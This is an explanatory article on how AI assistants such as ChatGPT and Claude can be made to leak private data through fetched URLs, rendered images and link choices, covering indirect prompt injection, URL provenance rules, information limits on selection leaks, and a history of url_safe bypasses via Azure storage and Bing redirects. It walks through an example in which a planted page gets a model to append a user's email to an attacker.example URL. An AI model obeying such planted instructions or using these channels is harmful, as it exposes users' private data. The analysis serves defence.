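# Which web addresses an AI assistant may fetch: the URL rules of OpenAI and Anthropic

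## How reading a web page can send private data out

AI assistants such as OpenAI's ChatGPT and Anthropic's Claude can read web pages while they answer a question. When a user asks for a summary of an article, the assistant's software requests the article's web address, or URL, and passes the text to the language model, the program that writes the reply. The assistant often also has access to private material, such as the user's earlier conversations, emails and work documents. Requesting a web page sends text to whoever runs the site, so an attacker who can influence which URL the assistant requests can use the request to obtain some of that material. Security researchers call this *exfiltration*, the sending of private data to a party who should not have it.

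OpenAI and Anthropic both respond to the risk, in part, by limiting which URLs their assistants may request without asking the user. Whether a URL is allowed depends on where it came from, such as the user's own message, a search result, or a crawler that had already found it on the public web. The companies have accepted different sources in different products and at different times, and that choice largely determines what an attacker can still do.

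### What a request carries

An AI assistant can read the web with a *search tool*, which takes a query and returns results with their URLs, and a *fetch tool*, which requests one URL and returns the page's contents. Claude's are called web_search and web_fetch. According to *Web fetch tool*, a page in Anthropic's developer documentation, Claude chooses what to fetch based on the prompt and the available URLs, Anthropic's system retrieves the full text, and Claude uses that text in its answer. If the user names a document without giving its address, Claude searches first and then fetches the result. In *The Memory Heist*, Ayush Paul (2026) explains how he got personal data out of the Claude app, even though he describes web_fetch as read-only by design.

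An ordinary request for a web page is of a type called GET, which web developers class as "safe". MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)*, an entry in a reference work for web developers, explains that a client making a safe request does not ask the server to change anything, but that the server can still log the request or keep statistics on it. The request is "read-only" in this narrow sense, which does not limit what the server may do with the information it receives.

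A web server can log the address that a visitor requests. In the invented URL `shop.example/search?item=boots`, `shop.example` is the domain, which identifies the site, `/search` is the path, and the part after the question mark is the query string, which can hold more or less any text. The request delivers both the path and the query string because the server needs them to work out what to return. Apache's *Log Files*, part of the manual for a widely used web server program, explains that the access log records every request the server processes. In the common format, each line holds the visitor's network address, the time and the full request line, including the query string. A site owner can therefore read a value that a visitor put into a URL by looking in the ordinary access log.

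Encrypting the connection does not prevent the leak. The security writer Daniel Miessler (2015) pointed out in *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS* that a secure connection encrypts the URL as it crosses the network, but the server that receives it often logs it. In an exfiltration attack, the attacker controls that server. For similar reasons, engineers have long considered it a mistake to put private data in a URL. MITRE, a non-profit that catalogues software weaknesses, lists it as one because query strings can end up in web logs, browser histories and the "referrer" information that passes from one site to the next. Another copy of Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* similarly warns customers whose data Anthropic has agreed not to retain that the publisher of a fetched site may still keep whatever the URL contained.

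Data can also leave without a fetch tool, through *link rendering*, the display of a link or image in the chat. The user's browser or app has to request an image from a server before it can show it, and that server may be an outside one. The software developer Simon Willison, who has followed these attacks for years, describes a common form in his running collection *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, in which the attacker gets the assistant to include an image whose URL contains the stolen data. According to the security company PromptArmor, messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram can also load a preview of a link in an assistant's message, which sends the data out without a click.

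*Silent Egress* (2026) measured such leaks in a test system that the researchers ran locally. Automatic link previews led to unintended outgoing requests with a probability of about 0.89. In 95% of the successful attacks, safety checks that examined the assistant's written answer missed the leak, so reading the chat is a poor way to find out whether anything has leaked. These figures come from one test system and are weak evidence of the odds in any commercial product.

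### Instructions the user did not write

Attackers can make an assistant put a user's email address into a stranger's URL through *indirect prompt injection*, which means hiding instructions in content the assistant reads. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the concept and demonstrated it on Microsoft's Bing Chat, among other systems. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes widely used lists of software risks, distinguishes it in *LLM01:2025 Prompt Injection* from direct prompt injection, in which the user's own input changes the model's behaviour. An attacker using the indirect kind does not need access to the victim's chat. Greshake and colleagues describe several ways to deliver the instructions: publish a page and wait for a search to retrieve it, email someone whose assistant reads the inbox, or trick a user into pasting the text. The model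 can read the instructions even if they are invisible to a person looking at the page.

Models follow such text because the user's request and the fetched page reach them as one long sequence. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) explains that a model cannot reliably use an instruction's source to decide how much weight to give it. The model may ignore the planted text on one run and obey it on the next. Newer models resist crude commands better than older ones did, but attackers have adapted. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people with plausible pretexts. Outside researchers reported one such attack to the company in 2025. It was written as a routine office email and worked in half of the tests.

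### From hidden instruction to server log

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives an example of the problem. An attacker controls a site and wants the assistant to request an address of the form `attacker.example/collect?data=`, with something private after the equals sign. Suppose this is the user's email address, which the assistant can see because it is helping with some correspondence.

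1. The attacker publishes a page with an instruction for AI models in its text. The instruction is to complete the address with the private item and load it.
2. The user asks an innocent question, and the assistant fetches the attacker's page in the course of answering. The instruction now sits in the same sequence of text as the user's question and the user's email address.
3. If the model follows the instruction, it writes out a new URL with the email address in the query string. This is a *constructed URL*, one that the model composed or altered itself and did not copy exactly from anywhere.
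4. The fetch tool requests the constructed URL. The attacker's server can return a blank page or an error for all it matters, because the email address travelled in the request.
5. The attacker opens the server's log and reads the email address.

The user may still see a good answer to their question. OpenAI notes that they may never notice the request, since it can happen in the background. The fetch tool and the server both work normally when they fetch the URL and log the request, and the fault lies in letting a stranger's text determine what the URL contains.

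### Two descriptions of the danger

An assistant is vulnerable when it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". In the example, the three elements are the email address, the attacker's page and the fetch tool. A fetch tool supplies two of the three, because it brings in the hostile text and also provides the way out. Willison thinks the only reliable protection is to remove one of the three, and that the way out is generally the easiest to remove. That seems right for an assistant that reads the web, since it would be much less useful without private data and could not browse without untrusted content. Willison also criticizes products that promise to detect most attacks. By the standards of web security, a filter that catches 95% of attacks fails, because attackers can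 keep trying until one gets through.

OpenAI describes the same danger in terms of sources and sinks, which it takes from conventional security engineering. A *source* is a way for an attacker to influence a system. A *sink* is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as following a link or sending information to a third party. An attack needs both. OpenAI compares the assistant to a customer service worker who can give refunds. The employer expects some callers to lie successfully, so it uses ordinary software to cap how much each worker can give away. In the example, this means accepting that the attacker's page will sometimes persuade the model, and limiting what the fetch tool will do when that happens. Willison would remove a capability, while source-sink analysis also allows a developer to keep it and restrict it, for example by limiting which URLs the fetch tool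 can open.

### Checking where a URL came from

Under a *URL provenance rule*, whether an assistant may fetch a URL depends on where the URL came from, not on which site it points to. A *link source* is a place from which a URL can enter a conversation, such as a user message, a search result, a fetched page or an email. Each rule accepts some link sources and rejects others, or checks the URL against an outside record. An *admitted URL* is one the assistant may fetch under the rule without asking the user. The central prohibition in Anthropic's developer documentation is that Claude "is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs."

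Such a rule stops the attack in the example between the third and fourth steps. The model has written a URL that ends in the user's email address and has called the fetch tool. Before any request goes out, ordinary software compares that URL, character for character, with the URLs that the rule allows. The attacker's page may well show the URL with the blank unfilled, but the completed URL does not appear on any page or in any search result, because the model has just assembled it in a private conversation. The software therefore refuses the fetch, and nothing reaches the attacker's log.

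The comparison blocks the constructed URL however thoroughly the attacker has persuaded the model and however often the model tries to fetch it. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, says Anthropic's rules block such URLs "deterministically". Earlier, in *Claude API*, Willison (2025) judged the ban on constructed URLs to be the part of Anthropic's policy that protects most against common attacks. For the block to work, code outside the model has to compare the entire URL, since a check on only the opening characters would let through private data at the end. Even then, the assistant's choice among admitted URLs can reveal something, though far less freely than a URL into which the model can write its own text.

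A list of trusted sites instead judges a URL by its domain. It would also stop the attack in the example, because the attacker's site would not be on the list. But it allows any URL on a listed site, including one with private data in the query string, and some reputable sites let outsiders collect data sent to the site. An attack on Superhuman, an AI email product, worked this way. Willison traces it to a setting that allowed images from a Google domain. Google Forms runs on that domain and stores data it receives through a URL, so an attacker's form could collect the contents of a victim's emails. Superhuman issued a fix. A provenance rule that bars constructed URLs would have blocked the request, yet it would allow an article on an obscure blog if an accepted link source had supplied the address. OpenAI has other objections to trusted-site lists, chiefly redirects and needless warnings.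 The two methods can also be combined. Anthropic lets developers add a list of allowed domains on top of its provenance rule, and Willison thinks this protects much better, provided that none of the listed domains can pass data on, which he admits is hard to ensure.

Training the model to refuse makes it less likely to attempt the leak. OpenAI says that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because safety training leads the model to refuse, and that its URL check, Safe Url, exists for cases in which the model is convinced, but it gives no figures. Written instructions to the model are even less dependable than training. *The Framing Gap* (2026) found that a broadly worded confidentiality instruction stopped the leaks in its tests, but that they returned when the instruction named particular behaviours and left out the catch-all. An attacker can look for phrasing that the training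 or the instruction did not anticipate, but phrasing has no effect on an exact comparison of URLs.

### What a provenance rule does not attempt

OpenAI says only that it prevents the assistant from quietly leaking user-specific data "through the URL itself". It states outright that this does not make a page's content trustworthy or keep misleading instructions off it. Security researcher Johann Rehberger, who had reported a leak of this type to OpenAI in 2023, likewise reads the company's technical paper as dealing with the exfiltration channel and making no claim about indirect prompt injection, in his Embrace The Red post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

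An injected instruction can therefore still distort the assistant's answer. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), by the security firm Trail of Bits, describes how researchers used a planted text file and a planted PDF to make an AI browsing agent state that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the moon and recommend a company that does not exist. This harm didn't require private data to leave in a URL. Greshake and colleagues had already listed manipulated content as a separate threat from data theft, with examples such as false summaries and search assistants that hide particular sources. A provenance rule can't prevent this kind of harm once it has allowed the assistant to fetch the page.

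Data can also leave by other routes, and each has to be blocked separately. An assistant that can send email can email private data to a stranger, and a rule for the fetch tool doesn't cover images in the chat window unless the company applies it there too. OpenAI says it has extended Safe Url to navigation and bookmarks in its Atlas browser and to searches and navigation in Deep Research, ChatGPT's tool for longer investigations. Rehberger worries that not every developer at OpenAI will know the check exists and use it in the next feature that loads a URL.

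## The threat the rules assume, and what a permitted link can still leak

The rules of OpenAI and Anthropic are designed to stop an attacker who can place text where the assistant will read it, and who owns a web server and reads its logs. *Silent Egress* describes this attacker as an outsider who controls pages on public websites, including the metadata that human visitors rarely see, and who may manipulate search rankings so that assistants fetch those pages more often. The attacker doesn't need to know the user's history or the company's instructions to the model. They can't change the assistant's code, read the user's encrypted traffic or insert messages into the chat.

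Such an attacker cannot access the user's data, but the assistant can. Security engineers call this a "confused deputy" problem, in which a program misuses its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who has none.

It is prudent to assume that the attacker can persuade the model completely. Models often refuse the attacker's instructions, but a URL rule only matters when they don't.

The rules assume that the attacker controls neither what the user types nor the company's backend, where the check runs. An attacker who could write the user's messages could approve any URL, and one who controlled the backend could switch the check off. The assumption about typing is less reliable, because users sometimes paste text they haven't read.

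### Content leaks and selection leaks

A provenance rule is meant to stop this attacker by ensuring that the user's secret did not influence the text of the URL. OpenAI reasons that if a URL already exists on the public web, independently of any user's conversation, it is much less likely to contain that user's private data. Anthropic's fetch tool for developers instead checks whether the URL has already appeared in the conversation, for example in a user message or a search result.

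In a *content leak*, the URL itself contains the private data, like the email address in the earlier example. In a *selection leak*, the URLs are fixed in advance, and the assistant's choice among them reveals the data. Suppose an attacker's page has one link for readers under 40 and another for everyone else. Neither URL contains anything private, but if the assistant knows the user's age and opens the matching link, the attacker can read the user's age group from the log. Comparing URLs character by character doesn't prevent this, because the assistant copied the link exactly.

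A model can leak information this way without doing anything it would normally refuse. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) tested four AI agents, including OpenAI's Codex, with three models. They planted an ordinary-looking reference link on pages the agents were likely to open. The link led to a site with links on different topics, and the agent's choice among them let the researchers infer what the user had asked.

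They scored these inferences by F1, a measure from 0 to 1 that penalizes both wrong guesses and missed items. Where the agents' choices left a readable trail, the average score was 0.89 for the concepts in questions from StackExchange, a question-and-answer site, and 0.80 for personal facts in a second set of conversations. Direct attempts to make the agents send private data succeeded 0.38% of the time. Four published defences, one of which filters what enters and leaves the agent's tools, lowered the scores by at most 0.03.

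None of the four was a provenance rule. The researchers also chose pages they had seen agents open in trial runs, so the results don't show how often an agent would come across such a link in ordinary use.

### How much a choice can reveal

An attacker who sees a request for one of N URLs can distinguish at most N cases. This information is usually measured in bits. One bit is enough to answer a yes-or-no question, and b bits can distinguish 2ᵇ cases. A choice among N admitted URLs that the attacker owns therefore reveals at most log₂ N bits, provided that the set of URLs did not depend on the secret. If the attacker can see the order of k fetches, there are Nᵏ possible sequences, so the limit is log₂(Nᵏ), or k log₂ N. The attacker may also learn something if the assistant stops early, but with 37 URLs and up to ten fetches, this adds less than a tenth of a bit to the limit.

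A constructed URL can carry far more. If the model can freely choose 200 characters from an alphabet of 64 symbols, each character carries 6 bits (2⁶ = 64) and the URL carries 1,200 bits. That length is realistic, since Anthropic's developer tool limits URLs to 250 characters.

*ZombieAgent*, an account by the security company Radware, describes an attack on ChatGPT that used 37 fixed URLs. A choice among 37 URLs carries about 5.2 bits, so it would take 231 such fetches to match the single constructed URL. OpenAI responded to the attack in December 2025 by restricting which links from emails ChatGPT may open, according to the news article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*.

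| What the assistant requests | Most the attacker can learn |
|---|---|
| One constructed URL with 200 free characters | 1,200 bits |
| One of 37 fixed URLs | 5.2 bits |
| Five fetches from the 37, in a known order | 26 bits |
| Ten fetches from the 37, in a known order | 52 bits |
| Ten fetches, no URL twice, in a known order | 50 bits |
| Ten fetches, no URL twice, order unknown | 28 bits |

A few bits can still do harm. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 20 bits, so four fetches, each chosen from 37 URLs, could in principle reveal it. About 33 bits can single out one person among eight billion, and one bit can reveal whether the user has a particular illness. Long secrets are much safer, since a 128-bit cryptographic key would take 25 such fetches, whereas the constructed URL has room for nine keys.

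Attackers may also get less information than the limit allows. When Liang and colleagues offered agents four links on distinct topics, the agents chose the right one in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal. With 16 links, the figure fell to 50%. If the errors were spread evenly over the wrong links, a choice among four conveyed about 1.6 of a possible 2 bits, and a choice among 16 about 1.0 of a possible 4. More links therefore made each fetch less informative in these tests. But the agents were choosing by relevance, and a model that has accepted explicit instructions might choose more reliably. A designer who assumes that an attacker can fully persuade the model should use the full limit to estimate leakage.

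Besides the choice of URL, the order and timing of requests can carry information. If an assistant always fetched the same ten pages but let the secret determine their order, the order alone could carry log₂(10!), or about 22 bits. Timing was the least accurate of the six signals that Liang and colleagues compared, with 58.6% of cases recovered correctly against 93.8% for the choice of URL.

### Fewer fetches, no repeats

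The limit k log₂ N is proportional to the number of fetches, so a cap on fetches is effective. Cutting ten fetches to five halves the limit, from 52 bits to 26, while halving the number of URLs saves only one bit per fetch. Developers who use Anthropic's fetch tool can set a cap with the max_uses parameter, which has no default value.

Inspecting requests one by one is a poor substitute for a cap. In its tests of content leaks, *Silent Egress* found that splitting the data across several requests reduced the leak measured in a single request by 73% and got past simple filters. A selection leak is even harder to catch with a filter, because no request contains any private text.

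Rehberger's Embrace The Red post proposes two measures against attacks that use a fixed set of URLs. OpenAI could cache each response for a few minutes, so that a repeated request gets the stored copy instead of reaching the attacker's server. Or it could stop the agent from visiting the same full URL twice in a session. Rehberger had not checked whether the company already did either.

Without repeats, the assistant has 37 URLs to choose from on the first fetch, 36 on the second and 28 on the tenth. Multiplying the ten numbers gives the number of possible sequences, which is enough to encode about 50 bits. That is only two bits fewer than with repeats allowed, because roughly a quarter of all ten-step sequences contain no repeat. Banning repeats does disrupt simple schemes that need to return to the same URL, but, as Rehberger says, it would still allow limited exfiltration.

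He also mentions that requests may arrive out of order, which matters more than repeats do. If the attacker could not recover the order at all, ten different URLs out of 37 would reveal at most 28 bits. But when the assistant reads each page before requesting the next, the requests arrive in sequence, so a company can't count on this protection. A developer also shouldn't rely on caching that serves another purpose. The cache in Anthropic's developer tool is there for performance, and Anthropic warns in the documentation that its behaviour may change.

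Liang and colleagues propose the more thorough defence of stopping the secret from affecting the requests. Their system downloads every resource linked from a page, whatever the user wants, and the agent then chooses among the local copies. If the outside requests were identical for every possible secret, N would be 1 and the limit would be log₂ 1, or zero.

The real system falls short of this because the agent sometimes needs material that it hasn't stored. The system then mixes the necessary requests with unrelated ones in random order. In the StackExchange tests, the attacker's F1 score fell from 0.89 to 0.39. The attacker still found nearly all the true concepts, but only 29% of its guesses were right, down from 87%. The defence multiplied the number of page fetches by 4.3 to 4.5, a considerable burden for a company that serves millions of users and for the websites that receive the extra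 traffic.

### Links that the attacker can renew

The same arithmetic gives a reason to exclude link sources that an attacker can influence. Suppose a rule admits any link that appears on a fetched page. Once the assistant opens one of the attacker's pages, the attacker chooses N, the number of links on it. When the assistant opens one of those links, the attacker's server can return a page with N new links, which the rule also admits. The server can generate each page on request, so the attacker doesn't have to prepare Nᵏ pages for k steps.

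This also undoes the measures in the previous section, except for a cap on fetches, which still limits the total amount leaked. If every step has new URLs, neither a ban on repeats nor caching ever applies. The requests can't arrive out of order, because the assistant doesn't have the next set of links until the server has answered the previous request. The attacker can also give each visitor a different set of links to keep their requests apart in the log.

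Renewing the links also lets the attacker use each answer to choose the next question. Liang and colleagues compared a single round of links with several rounds, each more specific than the last. When the private information was four levels deep, from a broad topic down to a detail, the several rounds recovered it in 49% of cases and the single round in 14%. Every link in their attack, starting with the planted reference, came from a fetched page, so a rule that excluded such links would have blocked the attack at the first step unless the URL was allowed for another reason.

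Paul's attack on the Claude app used the same opening, and Anthropic closed it by no longer letting Claude follow links it finds on fetched pages, as Willison (2026) reported in July. The blogger dyb estimated in *The Read-Only Lie* that each fetch could leak 4.75 bits, since every page offered 27 links. Roughly 30 fetches could therefore leak about 143 bits, which was enough for the user's name, employer and home city. The estimate comes from a personal blog, but the arithmetic is correct, and it shows that limiting each fetch to a few bits doesn't help much when the assistant may fetch dozens of pages in one turn.

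### Links that must exist in advance

Applied strictly, the argument would exclude search results and public indexes too, because attackers can publish pages and wait for a crawler to find them. The security company Tenable (2025) got past ChatGPT's check on displayed images by using its own pages that Microsoft's search engine, Bing, had indexed. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) concluded that ChatGPT's search results seemed to come partly from Bing's index and partly from OpenAI's own crawler. The hostile instructions can arrive through the same search results.

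The requirement to publish in advance does not keep N small either. Rehberger points out in his Embrace The Red post that a larger website or blog probably has a few dozen indexed URLs already, and that an attacker could go on to use thousands. With 4,096 URLs, each fetch could reveal 12 bits, so ten fetches could reveal 120, more than twice the limit for 37 URLs. Banning repeats would lower that total by only about 0.016 bits. A company that relies on an index therefore still needs to limit the number of fetches if it wants a low limit on selection leaks.

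Requiring indexed addresses helps mostly because the attacker has to prepare in advance. To leak one more bit per fetch, the attacker needs twice as many pages in the index and has to wait for a crawler to pick them up. If the assistant may follow links on fetched pages, the attacker can add as many links as they like during the conversation.

Pages in a public index are also easier to find and remove than links that exist only in one user's chat. The company that runs the index can look for a site with hundreds of near-identical pages, and removing them protects every user. Because all victims' assistants would choose from the same URLs, the attacker may also have trouble telling whose data a request carries.

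Under the rule, a page's owner can still change its text at any time after a crawler records the URL, even between two fetches in the same conversation. An attacker with indexed URLs can therefore adapt the instructions to what the model has revealed so far, but the rule stops them from adding new URLs in response.

A much stricter rule would admit only URLs from the user's own messages. Willison (2025) raised this idea when Anthropic released its developer tool, and was disappointed that the tool also accepts other sources. Under the stricter rule, an attacker would usually own no admitted URL, or only the one page the user had asked about. In the second case, the attacker could learn from the log whether and when the assistant opened that page, but the model would have no other URL of the attacker's to choose. The assistant also couldn't open a search result unless the user pasted in its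 address, which would defeat the purpose of asking it to research a question.

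## ChatGPT's check on displayed links and images, 2023 to 2025

OpenAI's first defence against this kind of leak dealt with how ChatGPT displays links. ChatGPT writes its answers in Markdown, a simple notation for formatting text that represents an image as a short code containing a URL. On 9 April 2023, Rehberger told OpenAI that an attacker could use such an image to take data out of a conversation without the user clicking anything.

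Others found the flaw too, including Roman Samoilenko, whose version used an image one pixel wide. Willison (2023) wrote about it that same month. OpenAI had no reward programme for security reports in early 2023, so Rehberger argued his case by email. He recounts in *ChatGPT Plugins* that the company called displaying images a feature and said it planned no change. According to the slides in Embrace The Red's *HackSpaceCon New Important Instructions*, six other products, including Claude and Google's Bard, had fixed the flaw by November 2023, while ChatGPT was still marked "won't fix".

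### Microsoft's short list

Rehberger had reported the same problem in Microsoft's Bing Chat on 8 April 2023. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, Microsoft told him on 15 June that a fix was in place, although his Embrace The Red post of 2026 dates the fix to May. As far as he could tell from outside, Microsoft relied at least partly on a *Content Security Policy*, a list of permitted addresses that a website sends with its pages. The browser refuses to load anything from elsewhere. Microsoft's list for images had four entries, all on bing.com, so the browser would not load an image from an attacker's server, whatever the model wrote.

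Anyone can read the policy in the browser and see what it allows, but it prevents the chatbot from showing pictures from the rest of the web. In *Trust No AI*, Rehberger (2024) lists eleven products in which he found the image flaw and recommends such policies to developers.

An image policy doesn't protect against links that the user clicks. Rehberger describes a 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office software, that put data from the user's inbox into a link in invisible characters. Clicking the link sent the data out. Microsoft fixed this in July 2024. Amazon fixed a leak in its Q assistant for businesses by not displaying links.

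### How url_safe worked

OpenAI acted in December 2023, in a different way. Rehberger noticed the change the morning after he had shown the leak working in a live demonstration, and he described it in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. In a note of 21 December, Willison (2023) welcomed the fix but found it "a bit weird", because OpenAI had not simply blocked images from outside sites. It had added a check called *url_safe*, which worked as follows:

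1. The model writes an answer that contains a link or an image. The client, meaning the website or app in which the user reads the chat, recognises the URL.
2. Before displaying anything, the client sends the complete URL to OpenAI's backend, together with an identifier for the conversation.
3. The backend applies OpenAI's criteria and returns a verdict, which is either "safe: true" or "safe: false".
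4. If the verdict is true, the client shows the link or loads the image, and only then does the outside server receive a request for the image. If it is false, the client leaves the item out.

Sending the URL to OpenAI for checking gives the company no new information, since its servers already process the conversation. In one of Rehberger's tests, the check marked a URL ending in an email address as unsafe, and the browser never contacted his server. He also saw that OpenAI could benefit from searching its record of these checks for signs of an attack.

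The check ran separately in each client, and OpenAI's iPhone, Mac and Android apps did not have it at first, as Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* explains. ChatGPT's tool for opening web pages had its own rule. Schwartzman's *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) says that the tool accepted only URLs that appeared in the prompt.

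### What outsiders could infer

The backend returned a verdict without a reason, so researchers had to infer the criteria by testing. Rehberger tested 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed. The check accepted the address for "a" and rejected the one for "d", although only that character differed. He speculated on Embrace The Red that OpenAI might be checking whether Bing had already indexed an image, and hoped it wasn't leaving the decision to a language model alone.

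All 36 addresses in his test were on the same domain, so OpenAI can't have decided by domain alone, at least for a small site it had no particular reason to trust.

It also showed that the check reduced the leak without stopping it. A choice among nine images carries about 3.2 bits, compared with 5.2 bits for all 36, and Rehberger sent the word "hi" as two images. An attacker could probably have leaked more per image by testing more addresses beforehand and keeping those that passed. At the rate Rehberger observed, 144 candidates would have yielded about 36 usable ones. He suggested that OpenAI limit each answer to one or a few images, which would have capped the leak as a limit on fetches would.

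Two years later, Tenable listed four factors that seemed to influence the verdict: trust in the domain, the presence and trustworthiness of a subdomain (a prefix such as `images.` before the main name), the presence and trustworthiness of query-string parameters, and the context of the conversation. Tenable inferred these from experiments and couldn't say how OpenAI weighed them. Researchers had much stronger evidence that a few domains passed whatever else the URL contained, and they used those domains to bypass the check.

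### Trusted sites with readable logs

Rehberger reported several ways to bypass url_safe to OpenAI in early October 2024 and presented them at that year's Black Hat Europe, a security conference. In Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*, he explains that an attacker needs a site that OpenAI's check accepts, that receives data through an ordinary GET request, and that lets the attacker read the data it receives.

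The check accepted GitHub, Microsoft's code-sharing site, so Rehberger could publish instructions there for ChatGPT to read. But he couldn't use GitHub to collect data, because only Microsoft can see the site's server logs.

Microsoft's cloud storage service met all three conditions. Any customer can rent space there, get an address under windows.net, and read a log of requests to it. url_safe accepted these addresses even when the query string contained private text. Rehberger's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, on Embrace The Red, names apache.org as a second domain that passed the check and let him inspect the logs.

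This was a content leak, and so far more serious than the nine images of 2023.

Researchers at the security company Zenity started using the same storage service in a similar way, as Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes. They first tried to send the data to a free testing service, but ChatGPT did not display the image. When they switched to Microsoft's cloud storage, the image loaded and the log showed the victim's API keys, the passwords that programs use to identify themselves. ChatGPT had found the keys in the victim's Google Drive through Connectors, a feature that links it to other accounts.

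In 2023, an attacker could use the flaw to obtain little more than the conversation in progress. By the summer of 2025, new features let ChatGPT also draw on earlier chats, stored memories and linked accounts, and a single image could leak material from any of them.

### Redirects through Bing

On 10 December 2024, Tenable told OpenAI about another exemption, which let every address on bing.com pass the check. Each Bing search result has a bing.com address that forwards the visitor to the listed site. Any site in Bing's index has such an address, including an attacker's. url_safe approved the bing.com address, and the browser then followed it to the attacker's server. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* calls this "an open redirect as a service".

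The model couldn't add private text to the forwarding addresses because they can't be altered. Tenable therefore had Bing index one page for each letter of the alphabet, and ChatGPT spelled out the data by displaying the matching images in order. This selection leak reveals at most one letter, or about 4.7 bits, per image. It is slow, but Tenable also got ChatGPT to store an instruction in its long-term memory that made every later answer, in every conversation, leak a little more data.

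The same exemption made phishing easier, in which an attacker lures people to a fraudulent site. url_safe also vetted clickable links, so ChatGPT could end a summary with a working link to a harmful page if the link used a bing.com address. Tenable suggests that users who trust ChatGPT may be more likely to click on it.

OpenAI had another safeguard. Tenable concluded from its tests that ChatGPT uses a second model, SearchGPT, to read web pages, and that SearchGPT has no access to the user's memories or conversation. A malicious page therefore couldn't get that data from SearchGPT. But SearchGPT's answer becomes part of the conversation, and Tenable found that ChatGPT could then follow instructions contained in the answer. At that point url_safe was the main remaining obstacle to a leak, and the exemption for bing.com removed it.

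Bing Chat's Content Security Policy also permitted images from www.bing.com. However, a browser applies such a policy to a redirect's destination as well as its starting address, so an address that redirected to an attacker's server should have failed in Bing Chat. OpenAI's backend checked the address in the answer, and nothing in the reported attacks suggests that it also checked where that address redirected.

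### When OpenAI and Microsoft made repairs

| Weakness | Reported | Repaired |
|---|---|---|
| Outside images in Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | May or June 2023 |
| Outside images in ChatGPT | 9 April 2023 | December 2023, in part |
| Trusted sites with readable logs | Early October 2024 | About August 2025 |
| Redirects through bing.com | 10 December 2024 | No date given by Tenable |

Microsoft took about ten weeks at most, while OpenAI took more than eight months to make a partial fix on its website. The later repairs were no quicker. On 1 August 2025, about ten months after his report, Rehberger publicly described the cloud storage leak because some of his bypasses still worked and OpenAI had not answered his recent questions about them. He left out the text of the attack.

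By then he had noticed that the url_safe call was no longer visible in the client, and he took this as a sign that OpenAI was changing the system. The change also made the check harder to study from outside, since researchers could no longer read its result directly. In a 2026 post on Embrace The Red, he confirms that further changes around August 2025 stopped the attacks he had shown at Black Hat, but he doesn't say exactly what OpenAI changed.

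The end of the Bing exemption is harder to date, but it lasted until at least August 2025. Tenable demonstrated a leak through Bing addresses with GPT-5, which OpenAI released that month. Tenable's advisory lists six requests for updates between 17 December 2024 and 4 March 2025, and states that OpenAI had yet to deploy a solution. In November 2025, Tenable reported that it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of its seven findings, but did not say which.

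### What a domain name leaves out

A domain name identifies the organisation that registered it, but not who controls a particular page, who can read that page's log, or where a request will end up. Microsoft rents space under windows.net to anyone who pays, and its search engine links to other people's sites. By trusting Microsoft's domains, OpenAI therefore also trusted the strangers who rent that space or run those sites.

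The mistake in url_safe also appeared in a suggested list of permitted sites for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Willison (2025) points out in *The Summer of Johann* that the list included azure.net, where anyone can rent a server.

OpenAI could have kept the list of trusted domains and managed it better. In Embrace The Red, Rehberger advised the company to tighten the list, publish it, and let business customers adjust it. Publishing it would have shown attackers which domains to examine, but they could already test any domain from their own accounts, and defenders would have gained more than attackers. It would have been harder to inspect every approved site for redirects and space that outsiders could rent, and to do so again whenever a site added a feature. A list short enough to inspect would also have excluded most of the web.

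In January 2026, OpenAI described a test that checks whether a URL is already public. This test would have stopped the cloud storage leak. It is less certain to stop a leak like the one through Bing, where every address existed in advance and none contained private data.

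## ChatGPT's rule against altering URLs, and its revision in December 2025

OpenAI used url_safe to check what ChatGPT displayed. In February 2025 the company launched Deep Research, which opens web pages itself, spends five to 30 minutes on a question, and writes a report that cites its sources. A user can connect it to Gmail and ask for a report that draws on both the inbox and the web, a combination that has all three elements of Willison's "lethal trifecta".

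### ShadowLeak

On 18 June 2025, Radware told OpenAI that a single email could make Deep Research leak data from the user's inbox. According to Radware's *ShadowLeak*, the email contains instructions that the user can't see but the model can read. When the user later asks for a report on the day's emails, Deep Research reads this one along with the others. It finds an employee's name and address in another email, adds them to a URL on the attacker's server, and opens that URL. The user doesn't click on anything and sees no sign of the request.

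This is a content leak, and OpenAI already had some defences against it. Deep Research refused Radware's blunter requests and sometimes searched the web for the suspicious URL instead of opening it. But its behaviour varied, so repeated attempts could succeed. It also avoided putting readable personal data in a URL, until the researchers got it to encode the data first. Radware thinks this worked because the software that handled the request received only a harmless-looking string. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests but doesn't give the number of tests.

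All of these defences depended on recognising something suspicious in the instructions, the address or the data.

The request also came from OpenAI's own servers. In the AgentFlayer attack, which Zenity described the same summer, the data left through the user's browser. A Content Security Policy or an employer's monitoring can catch a leak from the browser, but neither affects a request from OpenAI's servers, so only OpenAI could block this request.

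Radware observed no restriction comparable to url_safe on the URLs that Deep Research could open. This is surprising, because Schwartzman had reported in 2024 that ChatGPT's browsing tool accepted only URLs that appeared in the prompt. Perhaps OpenAI had not applied that rule to the new product. If so, it would be an example of Rehberger's worry that developers of new features don't use existing checks.

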